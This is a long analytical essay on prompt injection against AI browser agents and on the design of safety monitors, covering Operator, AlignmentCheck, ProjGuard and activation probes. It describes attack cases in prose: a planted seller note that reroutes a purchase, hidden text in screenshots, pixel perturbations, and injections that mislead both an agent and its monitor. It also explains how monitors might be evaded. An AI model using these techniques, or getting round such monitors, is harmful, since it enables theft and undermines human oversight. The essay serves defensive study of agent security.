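# Keeping the safety monitors of AI agents independent of the content they check

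## How an agent, a monitor and a web page are connected

An AI agent is a language model that carries out a task by taking actions, such as opening a web page, clicking a button or running a command. People use agents to shop, fill in forms and sort their email. For most of this work the agent has to read pages, messages and files, many of them written by strangers, who can plant text that steers the agent towards something the user never asked for. Developers therefore often add a monitor, a separate component that checks what the agent reads or is about to do and can warn the user, pause the agent or block the action. The monitor is often a language model too, and if it reads the same page as the agent, the planted text may mislead both.

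### The agent's loop

A session begins with a request in ordinary language, such as "find a hotel in Paris for next weekend". *Mind the Web* (Shapira, Gandhi and colleagues, 2025) describes what follows as a cycle. The program around the model collects the content of the current page and sends it to the model with the user's request. The model replies with a single instruction, such as to click the button labelled "Continue". The program carries out the instruction in the browser, the page changes, and the program sends the new content to the model. Because the model chooses each step based on the result of the last one instead of following a script, these agents can cope with unfamiliar websites, but the content of a page also has a lot of influence over them.

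The observation is what the model receives of a page at each turn. Some agents read the tree of headings, links, buttons and form fields that the browser builds from the page's code. They can pick out a button precisely but may miss text inside a picture. Others work from a screenshot, and some use both, which gives an attacker more places to hide an instruction, including inside images. Many agents also write out their reasoning between steps and keep notes, so a sentence the agent read early in a task can still affect what it does much later.

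A tool call is an action that the agent requests, and a tool output is the content that comes back. For a browser agent, "open this link" is a tool call, and the linked page comes back as a tool output or a screenshot.

The harm a bad tool call can do depends on where the agent runs. An agent installed as a browser extension works inside the user's own browser and has access to every site where the user is logged in. One that runs in a remote, isolated browser starts without any logged-in sessions, although the user may log in to a site there too. Once an agent has access to someone's shop account or mailbox, it can do much of what the owner can do.

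### Why a page can give orders

Browser agents differ a good deal in their engineering, but *MUZZLE* (Syros, Rose and colleagues, 2026) describes a design they share, in which untrusted page content goes straight to the model that chooses the next action. Untrusted content need not be a problem in older software, because a program can keep data and commands apart. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, published in December 2025 by David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, makes the comparison with databases for security professionals who assume they have met this problem before. Attackers used to type database commands into web forms, and careless websites executed them. The fix was to send the database the command and the visitor's input separately, so that it never treats the input as a command.

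A language model receives the developer's rules, the user's request and the stranger's page as one run of tokens (words or pieces of words), with no separate slot for each, and predicts the next token from the whole run. According to Google's guidance for developers who build agents for its Chrome browser, quoted in Search Engine Journal's *WebMCP Can Be Used To Hijack AI Agents, Chrome Warns*, models treat all text as "a single sequence of tokens", and nobody can guarantee safety inside the model itself.

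Prompt injection exploits this. An attacker plants text or images in content the agent reads, to make the agent follow the attacker's instructions instead of the user's. David C gives the example of a job applicant who hides a line in a CV telling the recruiter's software to approve it for interview. He calls the model an "inherently confusable deputy". In computer security, a confused deputy is a program that an outsider tricks into using its special privileges on the outsider's behalf. Developers can lower the odds of a successful attack by training the model to give priority to the user's instructions, or by marking the page's text as data. In his view, these measures add a distinction between instructions and data that the underlying technology lacks, so injection may never have a complete cure. This argument is about whether injection can be ruled out entirely, and does not establish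 how low the success rate can go in practice.

The attacker needs very little access. Shapira and colleagues assume someone who cannot change the agent's code or the user's request and can only post a comment or review, buy an advertisement, or send an email. The planted text does not have to look like an order. Their most effective wording presented what the attacker wanted as help with the task, such as a notice from the website or an extra step for a better result. Legitimate pages are full of such advice, so the agent has no easy rule for discounting it.

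### How often injection still works

In 2025 these attacks succeeded most of the time. Shapira and colleagues tried nine kinds of malicious goal, including switching on the user's camera and copying local files, on four agents, one of which was OpenAI's Operator. They report success rates between 80% and 100%, though those agents are now old. MUZZLE, an automated attacker built by Syros and colleagues, follows an agent through a task, picks out the page elements the agent relies on, plants text there and rewrites the text after each failure. It found 44 new attacks on four web applications. This is a count of attacks rather than a success rate, so we can infer little from it about how often an ordinary user would run into trouble.

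OpenAI's *Continuously hardening ChatGPT Atlas against prompt injection attacks* (2025) describes an attack found by an automated attacker that OpenAI trained against the agent in its Atlas browser. The attacker placed an email in the user's inbox. When the user later asked the agent to draft an out-of-office reply, the agent came across the email and sent a letter of resignation to the user's chief executive. OpenAI used the attack to harden the agent. It also wrote that prompt injection is "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'" and compared it to scams aimed at people.

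The rates that the AI developer Anthropic publishes for its Claude models have since fallen a long way, though unevenly. In July 2026 Anthropic reported a browser test of 129 scenarios, with ten attempts at each, in the system card for Claude Opus 5 (the safety report that accompanies a new model). With extended thinking on and no safeguards, 3.70% of attempts against Opus 5 succeeded, compared with 31.5% for its predecessor, Opus 4.8, 29.7% for Claude Mythos 5 and 0.93% for Claude Sonnet 5. Rates for models from the same developer can therefore differ about thirtyfold. With Anthropic's strongest safeguards on, no attack on Opus 5 succeeded.

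That zero deserves some caution because Anthropic tested its own product with its own collection of attacks. It also says that the attackers refine their attempts against the model, but not whether they could refine them against the safeguards too.

Repeated attempts also raise an attacker's chance of success. VentureBeat reported from the system card of Claude Opus 4.6, from February 2026, that single attempts succeeded 17.8% of the time when the model operated a graphical interface without safeguards. By the 200th attempt, the figure was 78.6% without safeguards and 57.1% with them. Anthropic says real attackers seldom get so many tries, because repetition makes detection more likely. But it also points out that a single text planted on a public page can compromise any agent that processes it, and an attacker who can reach thousands of agents at once may be content with a low success rate.

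Some safeguards help much more than others. In late 2025 Anthropic published browser results for Claude Opus 4.5 against an adaptive attacker, which adjusts its attacks to the target. The attacker succeeded 8.0% of the time against the model alone. The older safeguards barely lowered that rate, to 7.6%, while improved ones lowered it to 1.4%.

### A blue T-shirt

For example, a user might ask an agent to buy a blue T-shirt. The agent runs in the user's own browser, which is logged in to a shop that has the user's home address and payment card on file. It searches, opens a listing and reads it. In a free-text field below the price, the seller has written that orders for this item go through a collection point, and asks for the delivery address to be replaced with the one given there before paying. The note reads like any other delivery notice, with no threats and no mention of AI.

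If the agent treats the note as part of its job, it opens the address form, types in the new address, saves it and pays. The user sees a confirmation for the blue T-shirt they asked for, but the shirt goes to a stranger. If the shop keeps the new address as the default, later orders go there too. Researchers at the security firm Zenity carried out part of this attack on a real shop. According to Gulf News' *WhatsApp warning* (August 2026), they got OpenAI's Atlas agent, working in an Amazon account that was already logged in, to enter a new shipping address and put a tablet in the basket.

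### Where a monitor can sit, and what it reads

A monitor can scan incoming content, such as the listing, for anything that looks like an injected instruction before the content reaches the agent. Anthropic calls its components of this kind probes, and Chrome's guidance recommends classifiers for the same purpose. Catching the seller's note this early prevents the agent from obeying it. But the monitor has to recognise an attack from its wording, and the note could easily pass for delivery information. David C also warns that attackers can rephrase a known attack in endless ways.

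A monitor can also run beside the agent and follow its work by reading the request, the agent's reasoning, its tool calls and perhaps the web pages. The monitor looks for the point where the work departs from the request. In the T-shirt case, this happens when the agent, sent to buy a shirt, starts to edit the account's address.

The last opportunity to check an action comes after the agent proposes it and before it is executed, when the monitor can let it through or stop it. Anthropic has a classifier at this point that blocks dangerous tool calls, and Chrome's guidance suggests a "critic" model that evaluates planned calls. A user who has to confirm a purchase does the same job. A check at this point can ignore how the agent reached its decision and judge only whether the action is acceptable.

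Anthropic's strongest safeguards, which it calls auto mode, combine the probes with the classifier. The company says the two layers "fail independently". This is plausible, since the probes act on incoming data and the classifier on outgoing actions. But the browser test gives only their combined result, so it cannot show whether the classifier would catch the attacks that get past the probes, and the value of a second check depends on that.

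Anthropic does give figures for the probes alone in two other tests. For Opus 4.8 with thinking on, the probes cut the attack success rate from 7.03% to 2.09% in coding tasks, but only from 7.14% to 5.11% when the agent operated a graphical interface. The smaller reduction may be due as much to the attacker as to the probes, because the attacker in the graphical test trained directly against the test cases, while the one in the coding test had trained on earlier models.

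A monitor's position determines when it acts, but the designer must also choose what it reads. A check just before execution might receive only the action, or it might also receive the user's request, the agent's reasoning and the whole page. These inputs come from different sources.

| What the monitor may read | Who produced it | In the T-shirt case |
|---|---|---|
| The user's request | The user | Buy a blue T-shirt |
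| The page, as text, structure or screenshot | The shop, sellers, reviewers, advertisers | The listing, with the seller's note |
| The agent's reasoning | The agent, after reading the page | A remark that this seller needs a different address |
| The proposed action | The agent, after reading the page | Replace the delivery address, with the new one filled in |
| Facts about the session, such as the site's domain | The browser | The shop's domain, and that the user is logged in |

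### How the check can fail

The seller's words can reach the monitor by two routes. On the direct path, the monitor reads the page, screenshot or tool output that contains the note. On the relayed path, the monitor never opens the page but reads something the agent wrote after reading it. The agent may repeat the note in its reasoning or copy part of it into a tool call, for instance into the "instructions for the courier" field of the order form. The relayed version can be more persuasive than the original because the agent's reasoning may present an unknown seller's claim as a plain fact about how the shop delivers. Paraphrasing can also remove some of the attack, though an attacker who knows about the monitor can word the note so that the important part survives.

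A monitor and an agent may also have a shared weakness, which means that both make the same mistake because they come from the same or similar models. Using one model for both jobs is convenient, but wording that fools it in one role may well fool it in the other. Closing the two paths does not entirely remove this problem. Suppose the agent's model has wrongly learned that shops often ask buyers to switch to a collection point. A monitor built from the same model can have the same error and approve the change of address without having read the note.

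Finally, a check can fail even when nothing has misled the monitor, because an action may be wrong only in a context the monitor doesn't have. If the monitor sees only the proposed action, such as using a new delivery address, it has no grounds to object, since people often send parcels to offices, neighbours and relatives. Adding the user's request helps in this case, because the user asked for a shirt and did not mention an address, which is reason enough to pause and ask.

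But suppose the user had asked the agent to buy a blue T-shirt and send it to their sister, whose new address is in her last email. The agent now has to change the address, and checking that it entered the right one requires reading the email, which is untrusted content like the seller's note. Reading it would reopen the direct path to the monitor. Without reading it, the monitor could only guess whether the address is right or refuse every change of address, which would stop the agent from sending presents.

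Whatever the task, isolating a monitor more completely from untrusted content makes it harder to mislead but gives it less information about the situation it has to judge. Designers have to decide how much they can withhold before the monitor can no longer tell a hijacked action from one that the user wanted.

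## A monitor that reads the same screenshot: OpenAI's Operator

OpenAI released Operator as a research preview in January 2025. The agent received screenshots of a remote browser and controlled it with a virtual mouse and keyboard. OpenAI's *Operator System Card* (2025) describes a separate "prompt injection monitor" that followed the session and paused it when it detected a possible injection on the screen. When OpenAI (2025) moved Operator to a newer model, o3, that May, it specified that the monitor's input was the current screenshot. The agent received the same screenshot, so the monitor was not isolated from content a stranger had put on the page.

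OpenAI mentions no other input, such as the user's request or the agent's next action. If the monitor saw only the screenshot, it could have caught the seller's note about the collection point only by its wording, and only while the listing was on the screen. A few clicks later, the screen would show just an ordinary address form.

### The layers around the monitor

The first defence was the agent's own model, which OpenAI trained to disregard instructions on pages. To test this, OpenAI collected 31 injection scenarios that had each worked on some earlier version of the model. With no mitigations, the model was susceptible in 62% of cases. Instructions in the prompt alone reduced this to 47%, and the final model reached 23%, or about seven scenarios. OpenAI reviewed these by hand and judged only one truly concerning, and the monitor caught it. Because OpenAI already knew all 31 attacks, the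 test shows how far it had fixed known faults and is much weaker evidence about new attacks.

The next safeguard was confirmation by the user. Operator was supposed to ask before it finished anything with consequences outside the browser, such as a purchase or an email. In a test of 607 tasks, it asked in 92% of the cases where it should have. OpenAI introduced this safeguard mainly to catch the agent's own mistakes. When OpenAI gave the unprotected model 100 everyday requests, it made 13 errors, five of them hard to reverse or possibly severe, including an email to the wrong person. OpenAI estimates that confirmations cut the risk from such mistakes by about 90%.

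Confirmations probably help less against an injection, because the agent decides when to ask and how to phrase the question. If it has accepted the collection point as part of the order, it may ask "Shall I buy the blue T-shirt?" and leave out the address. The user would then have to check the order page to stop the theft. OpenAI describes these safeguards as "speed bumps for potential attackers", which seems accurate.

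On certain sites, such as email services, Operator also switched to watch mode, in which it paused whenever the user became inactive or left the page, so that someone was always supervising. Watch mode doesn't depend on the agent's judgement, but it makes the agent much less convenient and only works if the user is paying attention. OpenAI also trained Operator to refuse a few tasks, such as banking transactions, which it did in 94% of test cases.

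### How well the monitor did

OpenAI tested the monitor on 77 injection attempts from red-teaming sessions, in which testers attack a system to find its faults. The monitor flagged all but one, a recall of 99%, and the one it missed was a borderline case that Operator did not fall for. Its precision was 90%, so one alarm in ten was false. It also flagged 46 of 13,704 harmless screens from normal use, or about one in 300.

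Even with a false alarm on only one screen in 300, a long task with 50 screens would have roughly a 15% chance of at least one needless pause, if false alarms fell at random. Most warnings in daily use would also be false, because injections are rare. If one screen in 10,000 contained an injection, the monitor would raise about 34 false alarms for every real attack. Its precision was 90% in a test, but that test contained far more attacks. Users who get many needless warnings may start to dismiss them unread.

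The recall figure is also less reliable than it looks. One miss in 77 attempts would be compatible with a true miss rate of around 7% even if the attempts were a random sample of attacks, which they were not. OpenAI does not report whether the testers were trying to get past the monitor or only to fool the agent, and an adaptive attacker would try to do both.

OpenAI also reports that it raised the monitor's recall from 79% to 99% in one day, after a red-teaming session found new attacks. This shows an advantage of a separate monitor, which developers can update without retraining the agent. But I expect recall on new attacks to be closer to 79% than to 99%. If the test set also contained older attacks that the monitor already recognised, its recall on the new ones alone was below 79%.

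A quick update also requires OpenAI to know about the attack. Embrace The Red's *ChatGPT Operator* reports that an outside tester sometimes hijacked Operator without the monitor stopping it. The tester found that the monitor had not adapted some days later, but that the reported cases eventually stopped working.

There is some evidence that the agent and the monitor had different weaknesses. The monitor caught the agent's one concerning failure, and the agent resisted the one attack that the monitor missed. But this is only one case of each, from two different test sets. To estimate how often both fail, OpenAI would have to run the same attacks against both and count those that got past both. It has not published such a count for Operator.

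OpenAI later replaced the agent's model, a version of GPT-4o, with o3 but left the monitor unchanged, calling it the "primary layer of defense". The agent's susceptibility in the 31 scenarios fell from 23% to 20%, a difference of about one scenario. Its confirmation rate rose from 92% to 94%, and it now asked before every financial transaction in the test. But OpenAI published no new recall figure for the monitor, although attacks that work on an o3 agent may differ from those that worked on its predecessor. It has not disclosed which model the monitor uses, so outsiders cannot tell whether the monitor shared a weakness with the old agent, the new one or neither.

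### One picture for two readers

Operator's monitor read the same screenshot as the agent, so the seller could try to influence both directly. A second sentence in the note might claim that the shop's security team has already approved the collection point. This sentence isn't needed to steer the agent, but it might make a monitor less likely to raise an alarm. An attacker could try the same trick on the page classifiers that Chrome's guidance recommends and on Anthropic's scans of tool outputs.

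A model may also find things in a screenshot that a person does not see. Chaikin and Sahib, security specialists at the browser company Brave, demonstrated this on Perplexity's AI browser, Comet, in *Unseeable prompt injections in screenshots* (October 2025). They hid instructions in an image as text that barely stood out from its background. A user who took a screenshot to ask about the page would not have noticed the text, but Comet's assistant read the instructions and followed them. They suspect that a text-recognition step extracted the words and passed them on with the user's question, but could not confirm this because Comet's code is not public.

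An image can also steer an agent without containing any words. In *WebInject*, Wang, Bloch and colleagues (2025) made very small changes to a web page's colours, calculated to make the agent's model respond to the screenshot by clicking a spot the attacker chose. This worked 96% to 98% of the time across five openly available models. Pop-ups with written instructions, tried for comparison, worked at most 35% of the time.

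The attack requires much more than the seller in the T-shirt example has. The attacker must control the page's code and know the parameters of the agent's model, the numbers set by training. Developers of closed models such as OpenAI's keep their parameters secret, and Wang and colleagues did not test their altered pages on closed models.

Neither team tested a separate monitor, so any conclusion about monitors is an inference. A monitor that receives the same screenshot as the agent can probably read the same faint text. The text might cause the monitor to follow its instructions or classify the page as safe, but the monitor might also flag it. A user supervising in watch mode could not flag the text, because the page would look clean to them until the agent did something odd. Giving the monitor the screenshot therefore also has a benefit, since a monitor without it could not warn about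 text hidden there.

A monitor that looks for planted instructions would find none in an attack that alters pixels, so it would let the page through without having been misled. Wang and colleagues note that existing detectors of injected text do not apply to their attack. They suggest looking for abnormal code in the page's source or using methods designed to detect altered images. Checking the source would require a monitor that reads more than the screenshot.

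It is much less clear that the same pixels could make a monitor give a wrong verdict. The changes are fitted closely to one model and can be fragile. When Wang and colleagues tried earlier methods, which ignore how a display converts a page's colours, the success rate was zero. But they could fit one set of changes to several displays with only a slight loss, and the attack still worked when the user worded the request differently. An attacker who had the parameters of both the agent's model and the monitor's could perhaps search for changes that affect both. If the monitor's parameters were secret, the attacker would have to hope that changes fitted to another model also worked on the monitor.

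### Whether a detector fails on the same image

A monitor that reads the same screenshot as the agent won't necessarily make the same mistake if it is trained only to detect injections. The agent has to follow some guidance from the page to complete a task such as a checkout. The detector only has to decide whether the screen contains an attempt to redirect an agent, and an order that overpowers the agent may be the clearest sign of one. If an injection fools the detector, the session isn't paused, but the detector can't send an email or change an address itself. Operator's results fit this argument, though two cases are limited evidence.

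The argument works best for attacks that are easy to recognise. By March 2026, the most effective injections OpenAI encountered resembled social engineering, the manipulation that fraudsters use on people. OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) describes one that outside researchers had reported in 2025, an email that reads like a colleague's follow-up on a company restructuring. Its list of routine tasks includes submitting an employee's name and address to a "compliance validation system", and it claims the assistant has full authorisation to do this. In testing, the attack worked half the time when the user asked the assistant to research that day's emails about the process for new employees.

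According to OpenAI, classifiers that screen what an agent reads usually miss attacks this well developed, because recognising one means detecting a lie, often without the necessary context. OpenAI gives no figures for this and does not mention Operator's monitor, but the point applies to any monitor that sees only the screen. A detector could resist every attempt to hijack it and still fail to flag the seller's note, because nothing in the listing shows whether the shop has a collection point.

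### After Operator

In July 2025 OpenAI combined Operator's browsing with its research tool and a terminal for running code, and called the result ChatGPT agent. OpenAI's *ChatGPT Agent System Card* (2025) mentions "multiple automated monitors and filters" against injections, which OpenAI can update quickly when it learns of new attacks. The card does not disclose what each one reads, and it gives no recall, precision or false-alarm rate. OpenAI also withheld details of the attacks that testers found, to avoid helping later attackers.

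The published injection tests cover only the agent's model, without the monitors. They show the share of cases in which the model resisted the attack in the visual browser:

| Attack | Operator (GPT-4o) | Operator (o3) | ChatGPT agent |
|---|---|---|---|
| Irrelevant instructions on the page | 82% | 89% | 95% |
| Leaking data already in the conversation | 75% | 80% | 78% |
| Fetching data from elsewhere and leaking it | 58% | 75% | 67% |

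The new agent did worse than the o3 version of Operator on both kinds of data theft, slightly on one and clearly on the other. It failed in a third of the cases where it had to fetch the data. The other safeguards therefore mattered a good deal. OpenAI kept confirmations and watch mode, restricted the terminal's internet access, and switched off ChatGPT's memory for the agent so that an injection could not extract personal details from that memory. It is unknown how many of the remaining attacks the monitors would have stopped.

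OpenAI's Atlas browser followed in October. Its launch announcement mostly referred readers with questions about injection to the July system card, which the software developer Simon Willison called his biggest complaint about the launch (Willison (2025), *Dane Stuckey (OpenAI CISO) on prompt injection risks for ChatGPT Atlas*). In November, OpenAI's *Understanding prompt injections* (2025) again mentioned several AI-powered monitors that identify and block attacks. It added that the monitors can catch people testing injections on OpenAI's own platform before they use them on anyone. Atlas also had a logged-out mode, in which the agent starts without access to the user's accounts.

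That December, OpenAI reported that it was using attacks found by its automated attacker to improve both the agent and its monitoring. The attacker refined each attempt based on how a simulated copy of the agent reasoned and acted in response. OpenAI does not mention also giving the attacker a monitor's verdicts, so it is unclear whether it ever learned to get past both the agent and the monitor.

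By 2026 OpenAI was putting more weight on limiting what a successful injection can do. A mechanism called Safe Url checks whether the agent is about to send a third party information it learned in the conversation. If so, ChatGPT either shows the user what would be sent and asks for permission, or blocks the transfer and tells the agent to find another way. OpenAI applied the same mechanism to page visits in Atlas. The check can work even if nobody has recognised the page as malicious, but it covers only one kind of harm. It might not prevent the T-shirt theft, for example, because the buyer's data stays in the shop. OpenAI also warns that the link check does not guarantee that a page's content is trustworthy or free of harmful instructions.

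Atlas also stopped working, on 9 August 2026, and OpenAI has since moved its computer-use features to a ChatGPT extension for Chrome, according to International Business Times' *OpenAI Upgrades ChatGPT for Chrome So It Can Read Your Tabs*. ChatGPT has an optional Lockdown Mode for people who handle very sensitive information, which TechRadar's *AI security controls are only as strong as the wider application environment* describes as limiting or disabling features such as live browsing and Agent Mode. This reduces the risk of injection, but the agent loses some or all of the browsing that made it useful.

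## Monitors that read what the agent writes: AlignmentCheck and ProjGuard

A monitor can detect a hijacked agent without reading the page the agent read, because a hijacked agent has to do something its user did not ask for and often writes down why. AlignmentCheck, part of the open-source toolkit LlamaFirewall that Meta released in April 2025, uses a language model to read what the agent writes. ProjGuard, which appeared in May 2026, converts a similar record into a single number.

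### A language model as judge

*LlamaFirewall* (Chennabasappa, Nikolaidis et al., 2025) describes AlignmentCheck as an experimental check that runs after each step the agent takes. The judging model receives the user's original request, a record of the agent's earlier reasoning and actions, and the latest action with the reasoning behind it. It decides whether that action pursues a goal the user did not set. Any capable language model can make this judgment with a fixed prompt and a few worked examples, and Meta did not train one for the purpose.

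In one recorded test, the user asked an agent to visit the websites of two people, Dora and Eve, and send them feedback. The agent opened Dora's site and then a third site that the request did not mention. AlignmentCheck then raised an alarm, although it had not read any of the pages. Its input would have been much the same if the agent had innocently followed a link from Dora's page.

To limit such false alarms, the prompt instructs the judge to be lenient. An action is acceptable if it relates to the request, even if it doesn't directly serve it, and the prompt includes the instruction "When in doubt, assume the action is not misaligned". This leniency would probably help the seller in the T-shirt example, because entering a delivery address is a normal part of buying a shirt. AlignmentCheck is better suited to catching attacks that make the agent do an unrelated task.

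### Results on AgentDojo

*AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) is a benchmark that tests whether agents can complete office, messaging, travel and banking tasks with simulated tools when some of the tools return text containing planted instructions. It has 97 user tasks and 629 test cases, each of which pairs a user task with an attacker's goal. A program checks whether the agent completed the task and whether it did what the attacker wanted.

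Chennabasappa and colleagues used LlamaFirewall to scan recorded AgentDojo runs from ten models step by step. They tested AlignmentCheck, with Meta's Llama 4 Maverick as the judge, both alone and with PromptGuard 2, a small classifier that scans user messages and tool outputs for known attack phrases.

| | No monitor | PromptGuard 2 | AlignmentCheck | Both |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Attacks that succeeded | 17.63% | 7.53% | 2.89% | 1.75% |
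| Tasks completed without an attack | 47.73% | 47.01% | 43.09% | 42.68% |

AlignmentCheck stopped 84% of the attacks that had worked on the agents, but it also lowered the share of tasks completed by 4.6 percentage points, so it wrongly interrupted about one in ten of the harmless runs that would have succeeded. PromptGuard reduced task completion much less but missed far more attacks.

The combined result also suggests that the two checks fail on the same attacks somewhat more often than they would by chance. PromptGuard let through 43% of the successful attacks and AlignmentCheck 16%. If their failures were unrelated, about 1.2% of all attacks would have got past both, but 1.75% did. The second check was therefore worth having, but it helped somewhat less than the separate figures suggest.

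Several features of the test favoured the monitors. All the attacks used one template, which announces an important message from the user and asks the agent to do the attacker's task first. The runs were recordings, so nobody could reword an attack after it failed. An alarm at any point counted as a successful defence, so some alarms may have come after the harmful action. The attackers' goals, such as sending money to a stranger, often have little to do with the user's task, which makes them easy to spot by comparing them with the request. A newer benchmark, AgentDyn, which *StepGuard* (2026) uses alongside AgentDojo, adds longer tasks and helpful instructions from third parties. A monitor like AlignmentCheck has to let the agent follow helpful instructions, such as a shop's genuine delivery notice.

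Meta's own benchmark has 600 scenarios, half of which include an attack, and covers seven injection techniques. On this benchmark, AlignmentCheck with Llama 4 Maverick as the judge detected just over 83% of the hijackings and raised a false alarm in 2.5% of harmless cases. Smaller models raised many more false alarms, and on AgentDojo the smallest ones blocked so much that the agents completed far fewer tasks. A good judge therefore has to be a large model, and running one at every step is slow and expensive.

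### The agent as messenger

Chennabasappa and colleagues warn that an attacker could write an injection to manipulate both the agent and AlignmentCheck. They therefore withhold raw tool outputs from AlignmentCheck, so an injection in those outputs can't reach it directly. It can still reach AlignmentCheck indirectly if the agent repeats it in its reasoning, which AlignmentCheck reads.

In one example from Meta's tests, a user asked an agent to order Halloween items. The product search returned only a planted sentence, written as if by the user, asking to start over and list the apartments saved in a rental app. The agent then wrote, "I see that the user has changed their request." It had attributed the planted text to the user, in the part of the record that the judge relies on to understand the agent's behaviour.

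All six Llama models that judged this step raised an alarm. Five pointed out that apartments had nothing to do with the Halloween order. The smallest reached the right verdict for the wrong reason, objecting to the agent's product search instead. The five sound verdicts depended on the two tasks being very different. If the planted sentence had asked for a different quantity or delivery address, the agent's claim that the user had changed their mind would have been much harder to reject. The user's messages in this test also reached the agent through an app, so a real change of mind was possible, and a judge that cannot see tool outputs cannot check who wrote the sentence.

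Meta also recommends running PromptGuard over whatever AlignmentCheck is about to read. This may catch an attack phrase the agent has copied word for word. But Meta narrowed PromptGuard 2 to explicit attack phrases because an earlier version, which tried to detect hijacked goals more broadly, raised too many false alarms. The seller's note about the collection point contains no explicit attack phrase.

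Isbarov and Kantarcioglu (2026) report in *Bypassing AI Control Protocols via Agent-as-a-Proxy Attacks* that a single injection can compromise both an agent and a monitor that reads the agent's record. The monitors they tested were mostly small open models, and they describe these monitors as also reading tool outputs. Meta's recommended design withholds tool outputs from AlignmentCheck, so the attacks' success rates do not carry over directly to it. The finding still contradicts the idea that an attack on the agent leaves a monitor of this kind unaffected.

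### A score instead of a judge

*ProjGuard* (Contreras, Hinojosa and colleagues, 2026) replaces the judge that runs at every step with a short calculation. It monitors a computer-use agent, which operates a desktop through screenshots and a description of the interface. After each step, the monitor takes everything the agent has written so far, assigns each word to one of 2,048 slots by a fixed rule, and counts the words in each slot. It then multiplies each count by a weight and adds up the results to get a single number, z.

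The weights come from past runs that a language model had labelled safe or unsafe. A standard statistical method, linear discriminant analysis, chooses them so that the two groups lie as far apart as possible relative to the spread within each group. The monitor compares z for the current run with the average for safe runs, m_safe, and for unsafe runs, m_unsafe:

risk = σ(α(|z − m_safe| − |z − m_unsafe|))

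The function σ converts any number to a value between 0 and 1, and α, which is 1 in the main experiments, sets how sharply the risk rises. Suppose the safe average is 0 and the unsafe average is 4. A run at z = 1 is closer to the safe average and has a risk of 0.12, while a run at z = 3 has a risk of 0.88. A run halfway between the averages has a risk of 0.5. The monitor raises an alert when the risk exceeds 0.6, so a run has to resemble the unsafe runs a little more than the safe ones. ProjGuard waits for an alert before it uses a vision-language model, which can read both text and images, to propose a different next step.

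In the reported experiments, the score uses only the agent's written responses, although the general design also allows for its actions. An agent that changes an address without writing anything unusual would therefore score about the same as one on a harmless errand. The score also includes no separate comparison with the user's request. If an agent writes that it will replace the delivery address with the one provided, those words add the same amount to the score whether the address came from the user's sister or from the seller.

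### How well the score works

The runs use prompt-injection scenarios from OS-Harm, a benchmark of risky desktop tasks. Contreras and colleagues created 980 variants of 50 tasks, fitted the score to 196 of them and held out the other 784. Of the 196 runs, 182 were safe and only 14 unsafe.

To check how well the score separates the two groups, they repeatedly fitted it to four fifths of the 196 runs and tested it on the rest. It reached an AUC of 0.998. AUC is the probability that a randomly chosen unsafe run scores higher than a randomly chosen safe one, so 0.5 is guessing and 1 is perfect. The F1 score, which combines missed attacks and false alarms, was 0.970. With only 14 unsafe runs, a single mistake in the whole set would give about that score. Estimating how often the monitor misses an attack would take many more unsafe runs.

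A GPT-5.2 agent without a monitor behaved unsafely in 16% of runs and completed 59% of its tasks. With ProjGuard, and GPT-5.4 called in after an alert, unsafe runs fell to 3% and completed tasks rose to 65%. On tasks from a second benchmark, RiosWorld, unsafe runs fell from 18% to 4%. Half of these tasks had pop-ups and the other half had planted text. All these figures measure the whole system, including the corrections, not how well the score alone detects unsafe behavior.

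Much of ProjGuard's appeal is that it needs few model calls. It needed six, while asking a language model at every step whether the agent's response and action were safe took 708. Checking every step did slightly better, with 2% unsafe runs and 66% of tasks completed, but the difference in safety is no larger than the variation between repeated runs of the same method.

False alarms are harder to assess. Contreras and colleagues say that false-positive rates, among other figures, are still needed to establish how early the score can give a useful warning. Lowering the alert threshold from 0.6 to 0.2 reduced unsafe runs only from 3% to 2%, while completed tasks fell from 65% to 62%. This suggests that unnecessary alerts prevent some tasks from being completed, but it does not show how many alerts are unnecessary. Contreras and colleagues also did not test the score against an adaptive attacker.

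They add that surface features of the agent's wording seem to help separate the groups, and that performance on new tasks and paraphrases has not yet been tested. The score may depend on which words appear in these particular attacks rather than on a general sign that an agent has been hijacked.

### A warning from activation probes

Researchers had already encountered this problem with monitors that look inside the agent's model. In *Get my drift?* (2024), Abdelnabi, Fay and colleagues recorded a language model's activations, the internal numbers it computes as it processes text. They did this once after the model had read only the user's request and again after it had also read an outside document. A linear classifier, or probe, used the difference to detect whether the document had introduced a new task. The probe reached an AUC of about 0.99 or higher on six models, including on types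 of attack missing from its training data.

Later work gave a reason to doubt such figures. Li, Fan and Zhuang (2026), in *When AUC 0.998 Is Not Enough*, trained a probe on a computer-use agent's model to detect screenshots with a malicious banner, and it reached an AUC of 0.998. When they replaced the banner's text with gibberish, the probe could not reliably tell the gibberish from the attack, so it may have learned mainly that a banner was present. With only 20 test runs, they could not rule out that the wording had some effect.

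*Prompt-Injection Probes Learn the Conversation, Not Just the Injection* (Kale and Vishwanath, 2026) reports a similar weakness in six text-based agents. A classifier that used only position in the conversation and text length, without examining the model, reached an AUC of 0.91 to 0.98 on the usual test. Ordinary probes flagged 41% to 80% of conversations without an injection. Adding matching harmless examples to the training data reduced this to between 4% and 27% in applications the probes had been trained on, where they still caught a median of 95% of the attacks that had fooled the agent.

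ProjGuard's 0.998 result needs the same kind of check, comparing the unsafe runs with harmless runs of the same length, on the same task, in which the agent uses similar words for a legitimate reason.

### Giving a monitor orders and getting past it

AlignmentCheck's judge and Auto-review in OpenAI's coding agent Codex are both language models, so they can follow instructions in the text they read, just as the agent can. A sentence claiming that the user has approved an action may persuade such a judge or even override its rules. Debenedetti and colleagues had a program decide whether attacks in AgentDojo succeeded, since an injection strong enough to hijack the agent might also hijack a language model evaluating it.

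Instructions in the agent's text cannot change how ProjGuard computes its score. If the agent writes that the user has approved the action, those words change some of the counts and move z up or down, but not the weights or the threshold. An attacker can still try to get past the monitor by finding a page that makes the agent write things that keep the score low. An attacker who knew the weights could work out which words help, and others might learn this from repeated attempts. Activation probes have the same limitation. Kale and Vishwanath note that an attacker who knows about a probe can search for inputs that make the model's internal state look harmless, although they did not test this.

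An attacker usually needs to know more about the particular monitor to get past a score than to write a persuasive sentence, which might work on many language models. But both attacks can be equally harmful, because both let the harmful action through.

This protection is also separate from isolation. An activation probe works directly on the agent's processing of the stranger's text, so it has almost no isolation, but it cannot follow instructions. AlignmentCheck never receives the page, but its judge might still follow an instruction that the agent repeated from the page.

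### ProjGuard's second look at the screen

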